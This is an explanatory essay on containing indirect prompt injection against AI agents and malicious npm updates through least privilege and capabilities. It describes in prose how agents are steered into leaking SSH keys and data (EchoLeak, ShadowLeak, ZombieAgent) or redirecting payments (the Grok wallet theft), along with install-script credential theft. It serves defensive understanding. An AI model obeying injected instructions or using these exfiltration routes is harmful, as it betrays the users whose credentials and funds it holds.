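# Prompt injection and compromised library updates: how far permission limits contain the harm

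## Why injected text and a bad library update have the same reach

An agent is a program in which a language model chooses and calls tools such as file access, a shell, email or web requests. Attackers can turn an agent against its owner in at least two ways. One is prompt injection, which is text that makes the model follow an attacker's instructions. It is indirect when the text arrives in content the model reads while working, such as an email or a web page. Another is a compromised update, which is a new version of a trusted library that carries an attacker's code. Most programs load many third-party libraries, called dependencies, and many of these are transitive, meaning another library brings them in.

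Injected text and a bad library update both act with permissions the program already holds, so neither attacker has to defeat the operating system's access controls. An attacker who injects text only has to get a message in front of the model, while one who tampers with a library has to obtain somebody's publishing rights. In both cases, the harm they can do depends on the program's permissions, which are usually much broader than its job requires.

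### An invoice agent

A small company might use an agent to handle supplier invoices. The agent reads one mail folder, which a separate mail program fills. It records each invoice in one ledger file and sends payments through one accounting host, a server that accepts payment orders from anyone with the company's login. It loads an HTTP library to send web requests and a date-formatting library to convert suppliers' dates to one standard format.

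The developer built the agent from a general-purpose kit, so the model can read and write files, send web requests and run shell commands. The agent runs under the account of the employee who set it up. That account can start any program, contact any host, and read the credentials for other machines (SSH keys) and for rented computing services (cloud tokens).

| | What the job needs | What the account supplies |
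|---|---|---|
| Files | Read one mail folder, write one ledger file | Every file the employee can open, including SSH keys and cloud tokens |
| Network | One accounting host | Any host |
| Other programs | None | Any program |
| Credentials | The login for the accounting host | That login, plus whatever the SSH keys and cloud tokens unlock |

The libraries need even less access. The HTTP library needs only a connection to the accounting host. The date library takes a string and returns a string, so it needs no file or network access.

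### What code gets from the account it runs under

A process is a running program and the memory the operating system has set aside for it. Each process runs under a user account and carries that account's identity. When code in the process tries to open a file, the kernel (the core of the operating system) checks this identity against the file's permissions, then opens the file or refuses. Network access is usually looser. Unless an administrator has set up a firewall or a sandbox, an ordinary process can connect to any host the machine can reach. Programs started by the process normally carry the same identity, so a shell that the agent launches can open the same files as the agent.

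An SSH key is a file, and a cloud token is a file or an environment variable. Code needs only read access to copy either one and try to log in elsewhere with it.

When a program loads a library, the library's code goes into the memory of the same process. It then has inherited permissions, which are the rights that all code in a process has because the process runs under a given account with given credentials. A request to open a file reaches the kernel in the same form whether it comes from the agent's own code or from a date library. *Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System* (Ferreira, Jia and colleagues, 2021) describes the situation in Node.js, a system for running JavaScript outside the browser, and in npm, its package repository. Every loaded package can use the application's files and network connections, modify other packages, and generate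 new code while the program runs.

Archibald's *What happens when packages go bad?* describes how a hostile module on a developer's own machine could steal SSH keys, delete files or hold them to ransom, and search other projects for secrets. A passphrase or a second login factor makes a stolen key less useful. The example project, a small image-compression site, had 49 direct dependencies and used more than 1,700 packages, most of them part of the build system.

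An operating system could in principle give each library its own identity. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) offers a reason why common operating systems use accounts instead. If each file carries a list of who may use it, somebody has to keep that list current. An administrator can keep up with employees joining and leaving, but running pieces of software appear and disappear all the time. Designers therefore settled on the account, and everything that runs under an account has the same permissions.

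A tool call also runs with the account's rights. The model only produces text. The agent's program finds the tool name and arguments in that text and runs the corresponding function, either in its own process or in a subprocess. The kernel doesn't record whether the words that led to the call came from the employee or from a supplier's email.

Code in a compromised library can issue any request that its process may issue, while injected text can act only through the tools the model has been given. In the invoice agent, the shell removes this difference, because a shell command can read a key file, start a program or contact a host. If the developer had given the model only "record this invoice" and "pay this supplier", text in an email could affect little beyond the ledger and the payments, while the date library could still use all of the account's permissions. The two attacks have the same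 reach when the developer chooses to give the agent general-purpose tools.

### Ambient authority and the confused deputy

Suppose an email leads the model to call the file tool with the name of an SSH key instead of the name of a message. The tool requests the file from the kernel, which opens it because the account has permission to read it. The tool never specifies which right it is using or on whose behalf. Miller and colleagues use the term "ambient authority" for authority that a program exercises without selecting it. Their example is `open()`, the Unix function for opening files. The caller supplies a file name but no credential, and the request succeeds or fails.

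Hardy's short 1988 article *The Confused Deputy* shows what can go wrong through a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept its compiler in a directory called SYSX. Engineers had changed the compiler to log customers' use of language features to a statistics file in the same directory. To allow this, they gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write files in its home directory. That directory also held the billing records, in a file called (SYSX)BILL.

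The compiler also let users name a file to receive debugging output. One user learned the name of the billing file and supplied it. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which found the compiler's license and opened the file for writing. The debugging output then replaced the billing records.

Hardy finds a problem with each of the obvious repairs. The compiler cannot reject names in other directories, because users have good reasons to send output there. It cannot reject everything in SYSX, because someone with proper access to that directory might want output in it. Rejecting (SYSX)BILL by name leaves other sensitive files exposed, and someone would have to revise the compiler whenever a new one appeared. Tymshare added a system call that let a program choose between its own authority and the user's, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities, and other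 things besides files needed protecting. The last time Hardy wrote down the rule for opening a file, it contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

He concludes that the compiler worked for two parties, held authority from each, and had no way to specify which authority to use. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct until someone granted the license. A confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into using its legitimate authority on their behalf.

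The invoice agent's file tool is in the same position as the compiler in Hardy's example. It holds the account's rights for the employee's benefit, but takes file names from a model that has just read a stranger's email. A compromised library is a simpler case, which Hardy mentions in passing as the companion problem of the Trojan horse. A program gets the authority of whoever runs it, and code that is hostile from the start can misuse that authority without being tricked. The remedies for confusion and hostility differ in part, but in both cases the program can do only the damage its authority allows.

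### Capabilities and least privilege

Here, a capability is a right to use a resource or cause an effect, though writers on AI often use the word for a model's skill. The older literature also has a narrower meaning. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines a capability as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder may access the object the ticket names. In a system built on capabilities, each running program has a list of these tickets and can reach only the objects they name.

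Capabilities of this kind would solve Tymshare's problem. The compiler would hold one capability for the statistics file, and the user would give it another for the debugging output file. A user without a right to the billing file would have no such capability to give, so the compiler would not need to inspect file names.

Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* compares two Unix commands that both copy a file. In `cp foo.txt bar.txt`, the shell passes two file names to `cp`, which must open the files itself. Since the user might name any file, `cp` needs all of the user's file access. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`, which needs no other access to copy the data. `cat` still runs with the user's full authority, because that is how the system starts programs.

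`cat` could satisfy the rule of least privilege, but `cp` could not. Under that rule, every program and every user should operate with what Saltzer and Schroeder call "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". For the invoice agent, that set is the middle column of the table. Saltzer and Schroeder also recommend starting from no access and listing what to permit, a list now called an allowlist. They reason that a mistake in an allowlist tends to block something legitimate, which people notice, while a mistake in a list of prohibitions tends to let something through, which people may not notice for a long time in normal use.

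Widely used operating systems have been slow to follow the rule. Miller and Shapiro point out that a game of Solitaire needs only a window, some mouse clicks and perhaps one file for saved games, yet it could read the user's email and sell what it found without breaking any rule of the system. A feature called a "capability" doesn't necessarily follow the rule either. The POSIX standard for Unix-like systems defines "capabilities" as a fixed set of flags, and Miller and colleagues note that one of them lets a program change the ownership of any file on the machine. No combination of these flags can grant access to one particular ledger file and no other.

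### The threat model

*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) describes an attacker who can plant text in the emails, web pages, documents and tool results that an agent processes, without needing access to the model itself. The attacker may know which tools the agent has, and may aim to extract private data or to make the agent act for someone without authority, for instance by redirecting funds.

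Siu and colleagues exclude attackers who modify the agent's code, but Ferreira and colleagues cover them. Their attacker takes over a library developer's account through leaked credentials, a weak password or an offer to help with the project, then publishes a new version of the library. Applications that install the update are then at risk, even if they depend on the library only through other libraries. An application often has hundreds of transitive dependencies, and the attacker needs to compromise only one of their developers.

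Assume that neither attacker controls the kernel or the hardware. This matters because every permission limit depends on a trusted base, the components that must work correctly for the limit to hold. An attacker who controls the kernel can ignore any limit the kernel enforces. Kernels do have flaws, so the assumption can fail in practice. When a compiler or language runtime enforces a limit, it also becomes part of the trusted base.

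Harm can also occur without an attacker. *Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta*, a set of university course slides, pairs an untrusted source (an email, a web page, a dependency, a stale file) with a dangerous sink such as the shell or the network, and notes that either an attacker or an accident may control the source. Saltzer and Schroeder's first justification for least privilege was that it limits the damage from accidents or errors. The dissertation *Robust Composition* (2006) starts from a similar concern, that separately written programs combined to cooperate can instead interfere destructively with each other.

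The invoice agent's HTTP library might have a clean-up routine that deletes the library's temporary files. A mistake in an update could make that routine delete the employee's home directory. Confining the library to its own temporary folder prevents this, whether or not anyone intended the deletion.

### When someone decides a limit, and when it takes effect

A static limit is a restriction on what a program may do that someone sets before the code runs, whether a compiler, a runtime or the operating system enforces it. The word "static" tends to blur when a limit is set with when it is enforced, but this definition depends only on when it is set.

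Permission limits differ in when they are decided and when they are enforced. If a compiler refuses to build the invoice agent because the date library refers to the network, both happen before the program starts. An allowlist containing only the accounting host is also decided in advance, but the operating system enforces it at each attempt to connect, perhaps months later. If the employee is asked to approve each shell command, the decision happens during the run, when injected text may already have shaped the request on the screen. In Ferreira and colleagues' approach, library developers declare permissions, the developers who install the library accept them, and a combination of code analysis and run-time checks enforces them.

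Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of complete mediation, which requires the system to check every access to every object, is a strong argument for enforcing permissions at run time. A check made before the code runs can meet that standard only if it accounts for every way the code might reach a resource. This is hard in a language like JavaScript, where a program can create new code while it runs.

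A static limit must also be one that the process it restricts cannot edit. Saltzer and Schroeder ask whether a user named O'Hara could ever access file X. O'Hara's current rights don't settle this, because O'Hara might be able to change the rule for file X, or change who may change it. The same problem arises if the invoice agent's allowlist is in a settings file that its own account can write. One shell command can add a host, and the limit no longer holds after the next restart.

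### Notation

P is the process and c is any component of it, such as the agent's own code, a tool, the HTTP library, or the date library. A(P) is the authority of the process, meaning all the effects it can cause, and A(c) is the authority of one component. This use of "authority" follows Miller and Shapiro, who distinguish it from permission. Permission covers what a program may do to the things it can access directly, while authority also includes the effects it can cause through other programs. If Alice may read a file and sends Bob copies of the text, Bob has authority to read the file but not permission. A(P) therefore includes whatever a cloud provider will do for the holder of the employee's token.

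Without limits inside the process,

A(c) = A(P) for every component c.

The date library can open the SSH keys and send them to any host. In Node.js it may also be able to alter the code that issues payments, since packages there can modify one another. With limits,

A(c) = G(c) ∪ R(c),

where G(c) is what someone granted to c and R(c) is what other components pass to it. What they pass may be an open file or a login, or it may be an action they carry out on its behalf.

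For the date library, G(c) is empty and R(c) is small but not empty. The agent uses the library's dates, so a hostile version could still put false due dates in the ledger. The HTTP library has a grant for the accounting host, and the agent passes it the login with every payment order. A compromised HTTP library could therefore redirect money even if its limits kept it from reading any key on the machine. The permission system of Ferreira and colleagues lets components pass objects this way and makes the caller responsible for keeping sensitive ones from untrusted code. They consider it unlikely that a malicious update to a package without permissions will happen to receive the right object. That seems fair for a date library, but an HTTP library receives the login in normal use.

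Because R(c) depends on how other components behave, A(c) is usually impossible to compute exactly. In the capability systems that Miller and Shapiro describe, all access must derive from earlier access, so a component can never receive a right that no component connected to it had. The arrangement of permissions alone gives a cautious bound, which reliably rules out some actions by c but leaves others uncertain. Knowing how some of the components behave can rule out some of those too. *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) later proposed formal definitions of both notions, with separate bounds for what a component can do now and what it could eventually do.

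Miller and Shapiro also observe that "least privilege" does not specify whether to minimise permission or authority, and that the difference is enormous. A library with no permissions can still do damage if a component that has them carries out the library's requests.

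## How text that an agent reads becomes an action

An email can do harm only if the agent that reads it responds by calling a tool, because the email has no permissions and reading it doesn't run anything. Agents get from reading to acting through a simple loop, and the attacker's text enters partway through it.

### The agent loop

Suppose the employee types "process today's invoices". The agent's program then goes through four steps:

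1. The program assembles the model's context, which is all the text the model receives before it generates its next output. The context holds the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), a description of each tool, the employee's request, and a record of what has happened so far.
2. The model generates more text. If this text contains no tool call, the program shows it to the employee and waits.
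3. The program runs the tool with the rights of the employee's account.
4. The program adds the call and its result to the record, then returns to step 1.

Siu and colleagues write the choice of action as a formula. Let u be the user's request, H the record of calls and results, and M the agent's memory, which includes the system prompt and anything saved from earlier sessions. The action at step t is

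aₜ ∼ f(· | u, Hₜ₋₁, Mₜ),

where f is the model. The symbol ∼ means that the action is a sample from a probability distribution, so the same context can lead to different actions on different runs. Running aₜ produces a result oₜ, and the program appends the pair (aₜ, oₜ) to the record.

The attacker's text reaches the agent as oₜ. When the agent opens a stranger's email, the file tool returns the email's text, which becomes part of the model's input from the next turn onwards. It normally stays there for the rest of the task, so the first email the agent opens can affect the last payment it makes. If the agent saves a summary to memory, the text can also affect later sessions, which Siu and colleagues call memory poisoning.

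The kernel, which checks permissions in step 3, receives the call aₜ but not u or H. The agent's program could track where each piece of text came from, but in the plain loop above it doesn't, so only the model can treat a stranger's words differently from the employee's.

### Instructions and data in one sequence

Databases once had a similar problem. An attacker could type part of a database command into a web form, and a carelessly written program would paste it into its own command. Programmers can prevent this by sending the command and the form's contents separately, so the database never interprets the contents as a command.

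A language model receives the system prompt, the employee's request and the supplier's email through a single channel, as one sequence of text. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes language models as "lacking a formal way to distinguish instructions from data". Developers put markers around the different parts and can train a model to give the user's words more weight than words in a tool result. This learned preference makes some actions less likely, whereas a refusal by the kernel stops the action every time.

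The markers are also unreliable because a model can mistake punctuation in an attacker's text for a real boundary between fields, such as the one between a sender's name and the body of a message. The Hacker News' *New Agent Data Injection Attack Can Make AI Agents Misclick* (2026) reports on research into this problem from Seoul National University, the University of Illinois Urbana-Champaign and Largosoft. An ordinary program has strict rules about which characters end a field, but the models often accepted approximations, which could include a curly quotation mark or even a dollar sign. The model would then treat the words after that character as a separate email or tool result.

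A developer can't solve the problem by telling the model to ignore every instruction in an email. Invoices often ask the payer to quote a reference number, and the employee wants the agent to do so. Siu and colleagues give the example of an instruction to delete a particular file, which may be routine cleaning or sabotage. Which it is depends on who wrote the instruction and what the user asked for, and the model may have no reliable evidence of who wrote it.

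### Direct and indirect injection

Prompt injection is direct when the person typing to the model supplies the hostile text, usually to override the developer's instructions. It is indirect when the text comes from content the agent reads, such as an email. Siu and colleagues count a case as indirect injection only if the agent follows an instruction from an unauthorised source and the resulting action does not serve the user's task. By this definition, a hostile sentence that the model reads and ignores is only an attempted injection.

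An attacker who uses direct injection already has access to the agent and gains whatever the developer's instructions were meant to withhold. Indirect injection lets an attacker act with another person's rights, even without an account or any way to open a conversation with the agent. The invoice agent has one trusted user and reads a folder of emails from strangers, so it is mainly exposed to indirect injection.

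### One hostile invoice

Suppose an attacker sends the company an email that looks like an ordinary invoice. An extra passage presents the copying of a key file as part of the supplier's paperwork. An attack that succeeds would go as follows:

1. The mail program saves the email in the agent's folder. Nothing more happens until the employee next asks the agent to process invoices.
2. The agent opens the email, as its job requires, and the extra passage enters the model's context.
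3. The model generates a call to read the employee's SSH key, and the kernel allows it.
4. The key enters the context as a tool result. The model generates a web request that carries the key to a host the attacker runs, and no firewall blocks it.
5. The model goes back to the invoice and records it. The employee sees a normal entry in the ledger.

The model might well ignore the passage at step 3, but the attacker can send many emails and needs only one to work. Once the attacker has the key, somebody has to notice the theft and cancel the key, because switching off the agent doesn't stop the attacker from using it.

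Willison (2025), in a note on *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, lists three conditions for such a leak: access to private data, exposure to hostile text, and a way to send data out. The invoice agent cannot avoid exposure to hostile text, because strangers send invoices. It gets the SSH key and the open network connection from the employee's account, but doesn't need either to do its job.

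An attacker can redirect a payment even when the agent has only the access its job requires. For example, an email might lead the model to replace a known supplier's account number with the attacker's. The model then calls the payment tool, and the accounting host accepts the order. Throughout, the agent has only read its mail folder, used its own login and contacted the one host it needs.

An attacker may not need to give the model any instruction. The Hacker News describes attacks, which the researchers call agent data injection, that work by planting false facts. In one test, a product review reused the identifier of a real button on a shopping page, and browsing agents trying to open the full review clicked "Buy Now" instead. In another, a comment on the code-sharing site GitHub carried a forged author line. Coding assistants asked to apply a maintainer's fix would run a stranger's command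 if the developer approved what looked like a routine step.

An attacker might use the same method against the invoice agent by sending one email that the model reads as two, the second appearing to come from a regular supplier and giving new bank details. The model would follow only the employee's instruction to pay the supplier, but would send the money to the attacker's account. Strictly, this falls outside prompt injection, because only the employee has told the agent what to do.

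### From the first demonstrations to a benchmark

Early researchers of prompt injection assumed that the attacker was the person typing. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker plants instructions in text that the model will read. They attacked Microsoft's Bing Chat, which then ran on GPT-4, along with code-completion tools and test applications of their own. In the sidebar of Microsoft's Edge browser, Bing Chat could read the page on the user's screen, and the researchers found that text on the page could steer the chatbot even when the text was invisible to the user.

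They also described several ways an attacker could deliver the text, such as leaving it on a public page for a search to find, emailing it, or persuading users to paste it in themselves. A short passage could direct the model to fetch a longer one from elsewhere. They warned that an email assistant that can read and send messages could spread an injection from one mailbox to the next, like a computer worm.

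Greshake and colleagues compared processing retrieved text to executing arbitrary code. The comparison fits an agent with a shell. A chatbot with no tools has fewer ways to cause harm, though it can still mislead its user, for example by recommending a fraudulent website. Their demonstrations were individual examples, so they showed that the attack was possible but not how often it would work.

AgentDojo, which Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024, made that measurable. It simulates four settings: an office workspace with email and a calendar, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Each setting has a list of ordinary user tasks and a list of attacker's goals. The researchers paired every task with every goal in the same setting:

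| Setting | User tasks | Attacker's goals | Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 |

The banking tasks resemble the invoice agent's work. In one, the agent has to pay a bill stored in a text file, and one of the attacker's goals is to get as much money as possible sent to the attacker's account. For each pairing of a task with an attacker's goal, the benchmark places the hostile text where an outsider could plausibly write it and the agent will have to read it.

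AgentDojo scores usefulness and security separately, because an agent that refused every task would resist every attack. "Benign utility" is the share of user tasks that the agent completes without an attack. "Utility under attack" is the share of pairs of user task and attacker goal in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects. The "targeted attack success rate" is the share of pairs in which the agent achieves the attacker's goal. Ordinary code computes the scores from the final state of the simulated accounts and mailboxes, such as whether money has moved. Debenedetti and colleagues chose not to use a language model as the judge because the injected text might mislead it as well.

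Researchers were still using AgentDojo two years later. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) ran it on 13 models from six providers, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) puts the number of pairs at more than 900. AgentDyn, a newer benchmark, has longer tasks and, as *StepGuard* (2026) describes it, includes helpful instructions from third parties. It is a better model of invoices with reference numbers because an agent cannot do well by ignoring every instruction in what it reads.

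### EchoLeak

In January 2025, the security research group Aim Labs reported to Microsoft that it had got injected text past the safeguards of Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions from their organisation's emails, files and chats. A simulated bank cannot show whether such an attack would work on a commercial product. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the group's account.

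The attack began with an email, which anyone outside the organisation could send. The researchers covered many workplace topics in it so that Copilot's search would retrieve it for a wide range of questions. When an employee asked one of those questions, the email entered the model's context alongside the organisation's own documents. Its text led the model to select the most sensitive information there and put it in the web address of an image. The employee's browser tried to load the image automatically, which would send the information to whoever controlled that address. Ravia calls the attack "zero-click" because the employee never had to open the email or follow a link.

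Microsoft had several safeguards, including an allowlist of hosts from which Copilot's page could load images. The attacker's host was not on the list, but a Microsoft Teams service was, and that service would fetch any address it received. The browser contacted the Teams service, which then contacted the attacker's host. This illustrates Miller and Shapiro's distinction between permission and authority. The page had permission to contact only the listed hosts, but through Teams it had authority to send data to any host.

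The attack relied on Copilot's right to read whatever the employee could read. Ravia compares the email to a program with few privileges that gets a more privileged program to open protected resources for it. Hardy's compiler was in Copilot's position when it overwrote the billing file.

Microsoft registered the flaw as CVE-2025-32711. According to TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit*, Microsoft described it as "AI command injection" that let an unauthorised attacker disclose information over a network, with a severity of 9.3 out of 10. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) dates the fix to May 2025 and the public disclosure to 11 June. The EchoLeak attack was a research demonstration, and Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Willison adds that a dozen other products had already leaked data through links in a similar way, so the attack was new mainly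 because the user did not have to click anything.

### Other cases from 2025 and 2026

Researchers at the security company Radware demonstrated similar leaks from ChatGPT. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* describes two of them. The first, ShadowLeak, began with an email containing hidden text in a Gmail inbox that the user had connected to ChatGPT's research agent. The agent used its permission to read the inbox and open web links, and sent private data out inside a link. The data left from OpenAI's servers, so the victim's employer could not see it leave.

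OpenAI responded by preventing ChatGPT from adding anything to a web address. Radware's Zvika Babo then found a way round this, which he called ZombieAgent. The attacker's email supplied a complete address for each character, and the agent spelled out the stolen data by opening the matching addresses in order. The agent could no longer write its own addresses, but it could still choose which ones to open, and an attacker who can observe such choices can use them to extract data. Babo reported the flaw in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in mid-December.

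In a real attack on 4 May 2026, a thief stole from a cryptocurrency wallet attached to the X account of Grok, xAI's chatbot. A trading service called Bankr had created the wallet, and its agent, Bankrbot, carried out payment orders that it found in public posts. According to CryptoSlate's *Grok’s crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet*, the attack began with a post to Grok containing Morse code. Grok published a translation, which was a payment order addressed to Bankrbot. Bankrbot had permission to make transfers from the wallet, and it sent the attacker 3 billion DRB tokens, worth roughly $155,000 to $200,000. Bankr's developer later said that 80% of the funds had been returned.

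The attacker never had the wallet's private keys. Bankr gives control of each wallet to whoever controls the matching X account, and the order came from Grok's account. A check on the sender would have passed, even though the words originated with the attacker. An older version of Bankrbot ignored Grok's replies for this reason, but the developer left that rule out when rewriting the agent.

A digital membership token apparently widened the wallet's transfer rights, but accounts differ on whether the attacker put it there. CryptoSlate reports that the attacker found the token already in Grok's wallet, while the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1556* says the attacker sent it there first. If the second version is right, a stranger could relax the wallet's limits by sending it such a token. This would be the same weakness as an allowlist that the restricted program can edit, except that here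 an outsider could make the change.

Hostile or unwanted instructions can also come from a service the agent has good reason to contact. The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026) reports that a developer's routine queries to Alibaba Cloud began to return error messages with instructions for AI agents. The instructions were to provide the computer's login name, its public network address, the agent's own operating instructions and a list of its tools. An agent that complied would have used its permission to read local settings and send web requests.

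The company confirmed that it had sent the messages, described them as a measure against automated abuse, and said it would stop returning them as prompts. A supplier had used them in a live service, but there is no evidence that any agent handed over the data. The developer checked the server's certificate, which was valid, so the text apparently came from Alibaba Cloud itself. An allowlist containing only the company's own servers would have allowed the text through. The invoice agent is exposed to its accounting host in the same way, because the host's error messages also go into the model's context.

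Reports of other real attacks are less well supported. In Clubic's *Une phrase cachée dans un mail suffit à manipuler une IA*, Adrien Merveille of the security company Check Point describes an unnamed firm whose agents read its security logs. Intruders reportedly put an instruction in their web requests, which the logs recorded, and the agents then stopped logging the intruders' activity. According to OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026), the security company Zscaler documented two live campaigns in which hidden text on websites led agents to make payments. Merveille's account is second-hand and the OECD text is a machine-generated summary, so neither is strong evidence on its own.

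Google searched a large public archive of web pages for injected text. SecurityWeek summarises the results as pranks, attempts to influence search results, efforts to keep AI agents away, some helpful guidance and a few malicious attempts. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* quotes one of the malicious attempts, an instruction to email the contents of the user's SSH folder. Google found few advanced attacks and took this as a sign that attackers were not yet using the published research at scale. But the archive contains no private email, and Google left social media for a separate study, so the search could not have found the email behind EchoLeak or the post used to empty Grok's wallet.

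## How a library update becomes an action

A library update is already code, so the attacker only needs a machine to download and run it, whereas injected text has no effect until a model responds to it. Package managers, the programs that install libraries, often download and run updates without asking anyone. The cases below come from npm, though attackers have poisoned Python libraries in much the same way.

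### From a maintainer's account to the registry

Every library has one or more maintainers, who have the right to release new versions. To publish, a maintainer sends a package to the registry, the server that stores every version, together with proof of that right. The proof may be a logged-in session or an access token, a password-like string that scripts can use. The registry checks the proof but not whether the package matches the project's public source code, so whoever has the proof can publish anything under the library's name.

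Some tokens stay valid for a long time, and a thief can copy them. npm's alternative, Trusted Publishing, lets a maintainer name a GitHub repository and a workflow file (a script that GitHub runs on its servers). When the workflow runs, GitHub confirms the workflow's identity to npm, and npm issues a publishing credential that expires within minutes.

Help Net Security's *npm Trusted Publishing flaw exposed 1,500+ npm packages to takeover* (2026) describes how an attacker could have used this system without stealing anything. npm recorded each repository by name, and a GitHub repository's name can become free when the owner renames, moves or deletes it. An attacker could register the free name, add a workflow file with the right filename and receive a credential for somebody else's package. GitHub also sent npm the repository's permanent ID number, but npm didn't check it. Like Tymshare's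 compiler, npm relied on a name when it needed a right tied to one particular thing. Researchers at Bloom Security found more than 1,500 exposed packages. GitHub, which owns npm, announced a fix on 2 October 2026, and nobody knows whether an attacker had used the flaw by then.

### How a new version reaches a program

The invoice agent has a manifest, a file called `package.json` that lists the libraries it needs and the acceptable versions of each. Version numbers have three parts. By convention, developers raise the last part for a bug fix, the middle part for a new feature, and the first part for a change that may break programs using the library. A manifest can name one exact version or a range:

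| Entry in the manifest | Versions npm may install |
|---|---|
| `1.14.0` | 1.14.0 only |
| `~1.14.0` | 1.14.0 or later, but below 1.15.0 |
| `^1.14.0` | 1.14.0 or later, but below 2.0.0 |
| `^0.30.0` | 0.30.0 or later, but below 0.31.0 |

When a range allows several versions, npm prefers the newest, as research!rsc's *What NPM Should Do Today To Stop A New Colors Attack Tomorrow* (2022) explains. If V(t) is the set of versions in the registry at time t, and r is the range in the manifest, a fresh install normally gives

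installed version = max(V(t) ∩ r).

The agent's developer chooses r, but the library's maintainer controls V(t), so two installs from the same manifest can produce different programs. Anyone who can publish as the maintainer can decide what goes into the later install.

The same rule applies to transitive dependencies. If the date library depends on a small text-parsing library, the date library's manifest sets the range of parser versions it accepts, and the company may never have heard of the parser or its maintainer. The risk grows with the number of packages. If each of n packages had the same independent chance p of a hostile release in a given year, the chance of at least one would be 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ. For the 1,700 packages in Archibald's example project, an invented p of 1 in 100,000 gives about 1.7% a year. The real risks aren't independent, because one maintainer often controls many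 packages.

A lockfile removes much of this uncertainty. It records the exact version of every package in the program, including transitive ones, with a fingerprint of each package's contents. As long as the developer installs from the lockfile, a new release doesn't change the code that gets installed.

But a lockfile only protects the project it belongs to. When someone installs a library or command-line tool from npm, npm ignores the developers' lockfile and works out the dependency versions again. research!rsc says that "lock files are not transitive". Even if a tool's developers tested it thoroughly, its users may receive different library versions from the ones tested.

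Lockfiles also change. Many companies use update bots, such as Dependabot and Renovate, which detect new releases and propose updated lockfiles. If the company's server tests each proposal automatically, it must install the new version first, so hostile code can run there before anyone has reviewed the proposal. After the axios attack, Microsoft (2026) advised developers to restrict these bots for critical packages, replace version ranges with exact versions, and use npm's "overrides" setting to pin transitive dependencies too.

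In the Go programming language, by contrast, each package states the minimum version it needs of every dependency, and the build uses that version unless another package in the program requires a newer one. A program therefore doesn't get a new release until some developer asks for it. This also delays security fixes, which is the usual argument against this approach and against delaying updates in general.

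### Installation, import and call

Once the package arrives, its code can run at three moments, and the permissions available may differ between them.

When npm installs a package, it can run an install script, which is code in the package that runs before the program itself starts. Legitimate libraries use install scripts to compile parts of themselves or download extra files. The script runs under the account of whoever started the installation. On the employee's laptop, it can read the SSH keys and cloud tokens. On a build server, which assembles and tests a program whenever someone changes it, the script can use the build job's credentials, which may allow it to publish software.

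Attackers can sometimes run code during installation without declaring an install script. ilSoftware.it's *GitHub, il malware si nasconde dove la ricerca non guarda* reports on a worm from October 2026 whose packages contained a configuration file for compiling code. The attackers had put a command in this file, and the command ran during installation even though the manifest listed no install script.

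When a program imports a library, Node.js runs any of the library's code that isn't inside a function. This code runs in the program's own process, with the permissions that process inherited. Tests and build tools import libraries too, usually under a developer's account or on a build server.

At call time, the program runs one of the library's functions. The function runs in the same process and with the same permissions as the library's code did at import, but it also receives whatever the program passes to it. A hostile version of the invoice agent's HTTP library could behave normally until the first payment, then copy the login sent with the payment order. Someone who tested the update only by installing and loading it would see nothing wrong.

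During installation, hostile code in a library can do anything the installing process can do. After the agent imports the library, the code can do anything the agent's process can do, unless limits inside that process restrict it. Suppose the company moves the agent to a new account that can do only what the job needs. Hostile code can then do less after import, but if the employee still runs the installation from the old account, it can do as much as before during installation.

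This happened to users of Tensorlake, a service that runs agents and the code they write in isolated environments. According to Mishcon de Reya's *Shai-Hulud Burrows Into The Software Supply Chain* (2026), researchers found a malicious release of Tensorlake's npm library on 8 October 2026. Developers install this library on their own machines and build servers, outside the isolated environments. The release's install script searched those machines for credentials, even if the developer never imported the library or ran anything on Tensorlake.

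An agent with a shell can start an installation itself. Based on its telemetry at dozens of organisations, Bloom estimates that agents install about 70 packages a month on a typical machine and close to 350 on a developer's, not counting dependencies. Help Net Security adds that usually nobody reviews these packages before the agent installs them.

### Axios, 31 March 2026

The invoice agent's HTTP library could easily be Axios, a JavaScript library for sending web requests. Axios probably has close to 100 million downloads a week, though published figures differ by a factor of 100. *Supply Chain Attack on Axios Pulls Malicious Dependency from npm* (Willison, 2026) gives 101 million, and two package indexes roughly agree. Snyk listed 93.1 million a week in June 2026, and ecosyste.ms counted 479.8 million in the month to 19 June, or about 110 million a week. Datadog Security Labs' *Compromised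 axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (2026) gives over 3 million a week, Microsoft over 70 million and Techzine over 300 million. None of these figures measure the number of users, since one build server may download the same library many times a day.

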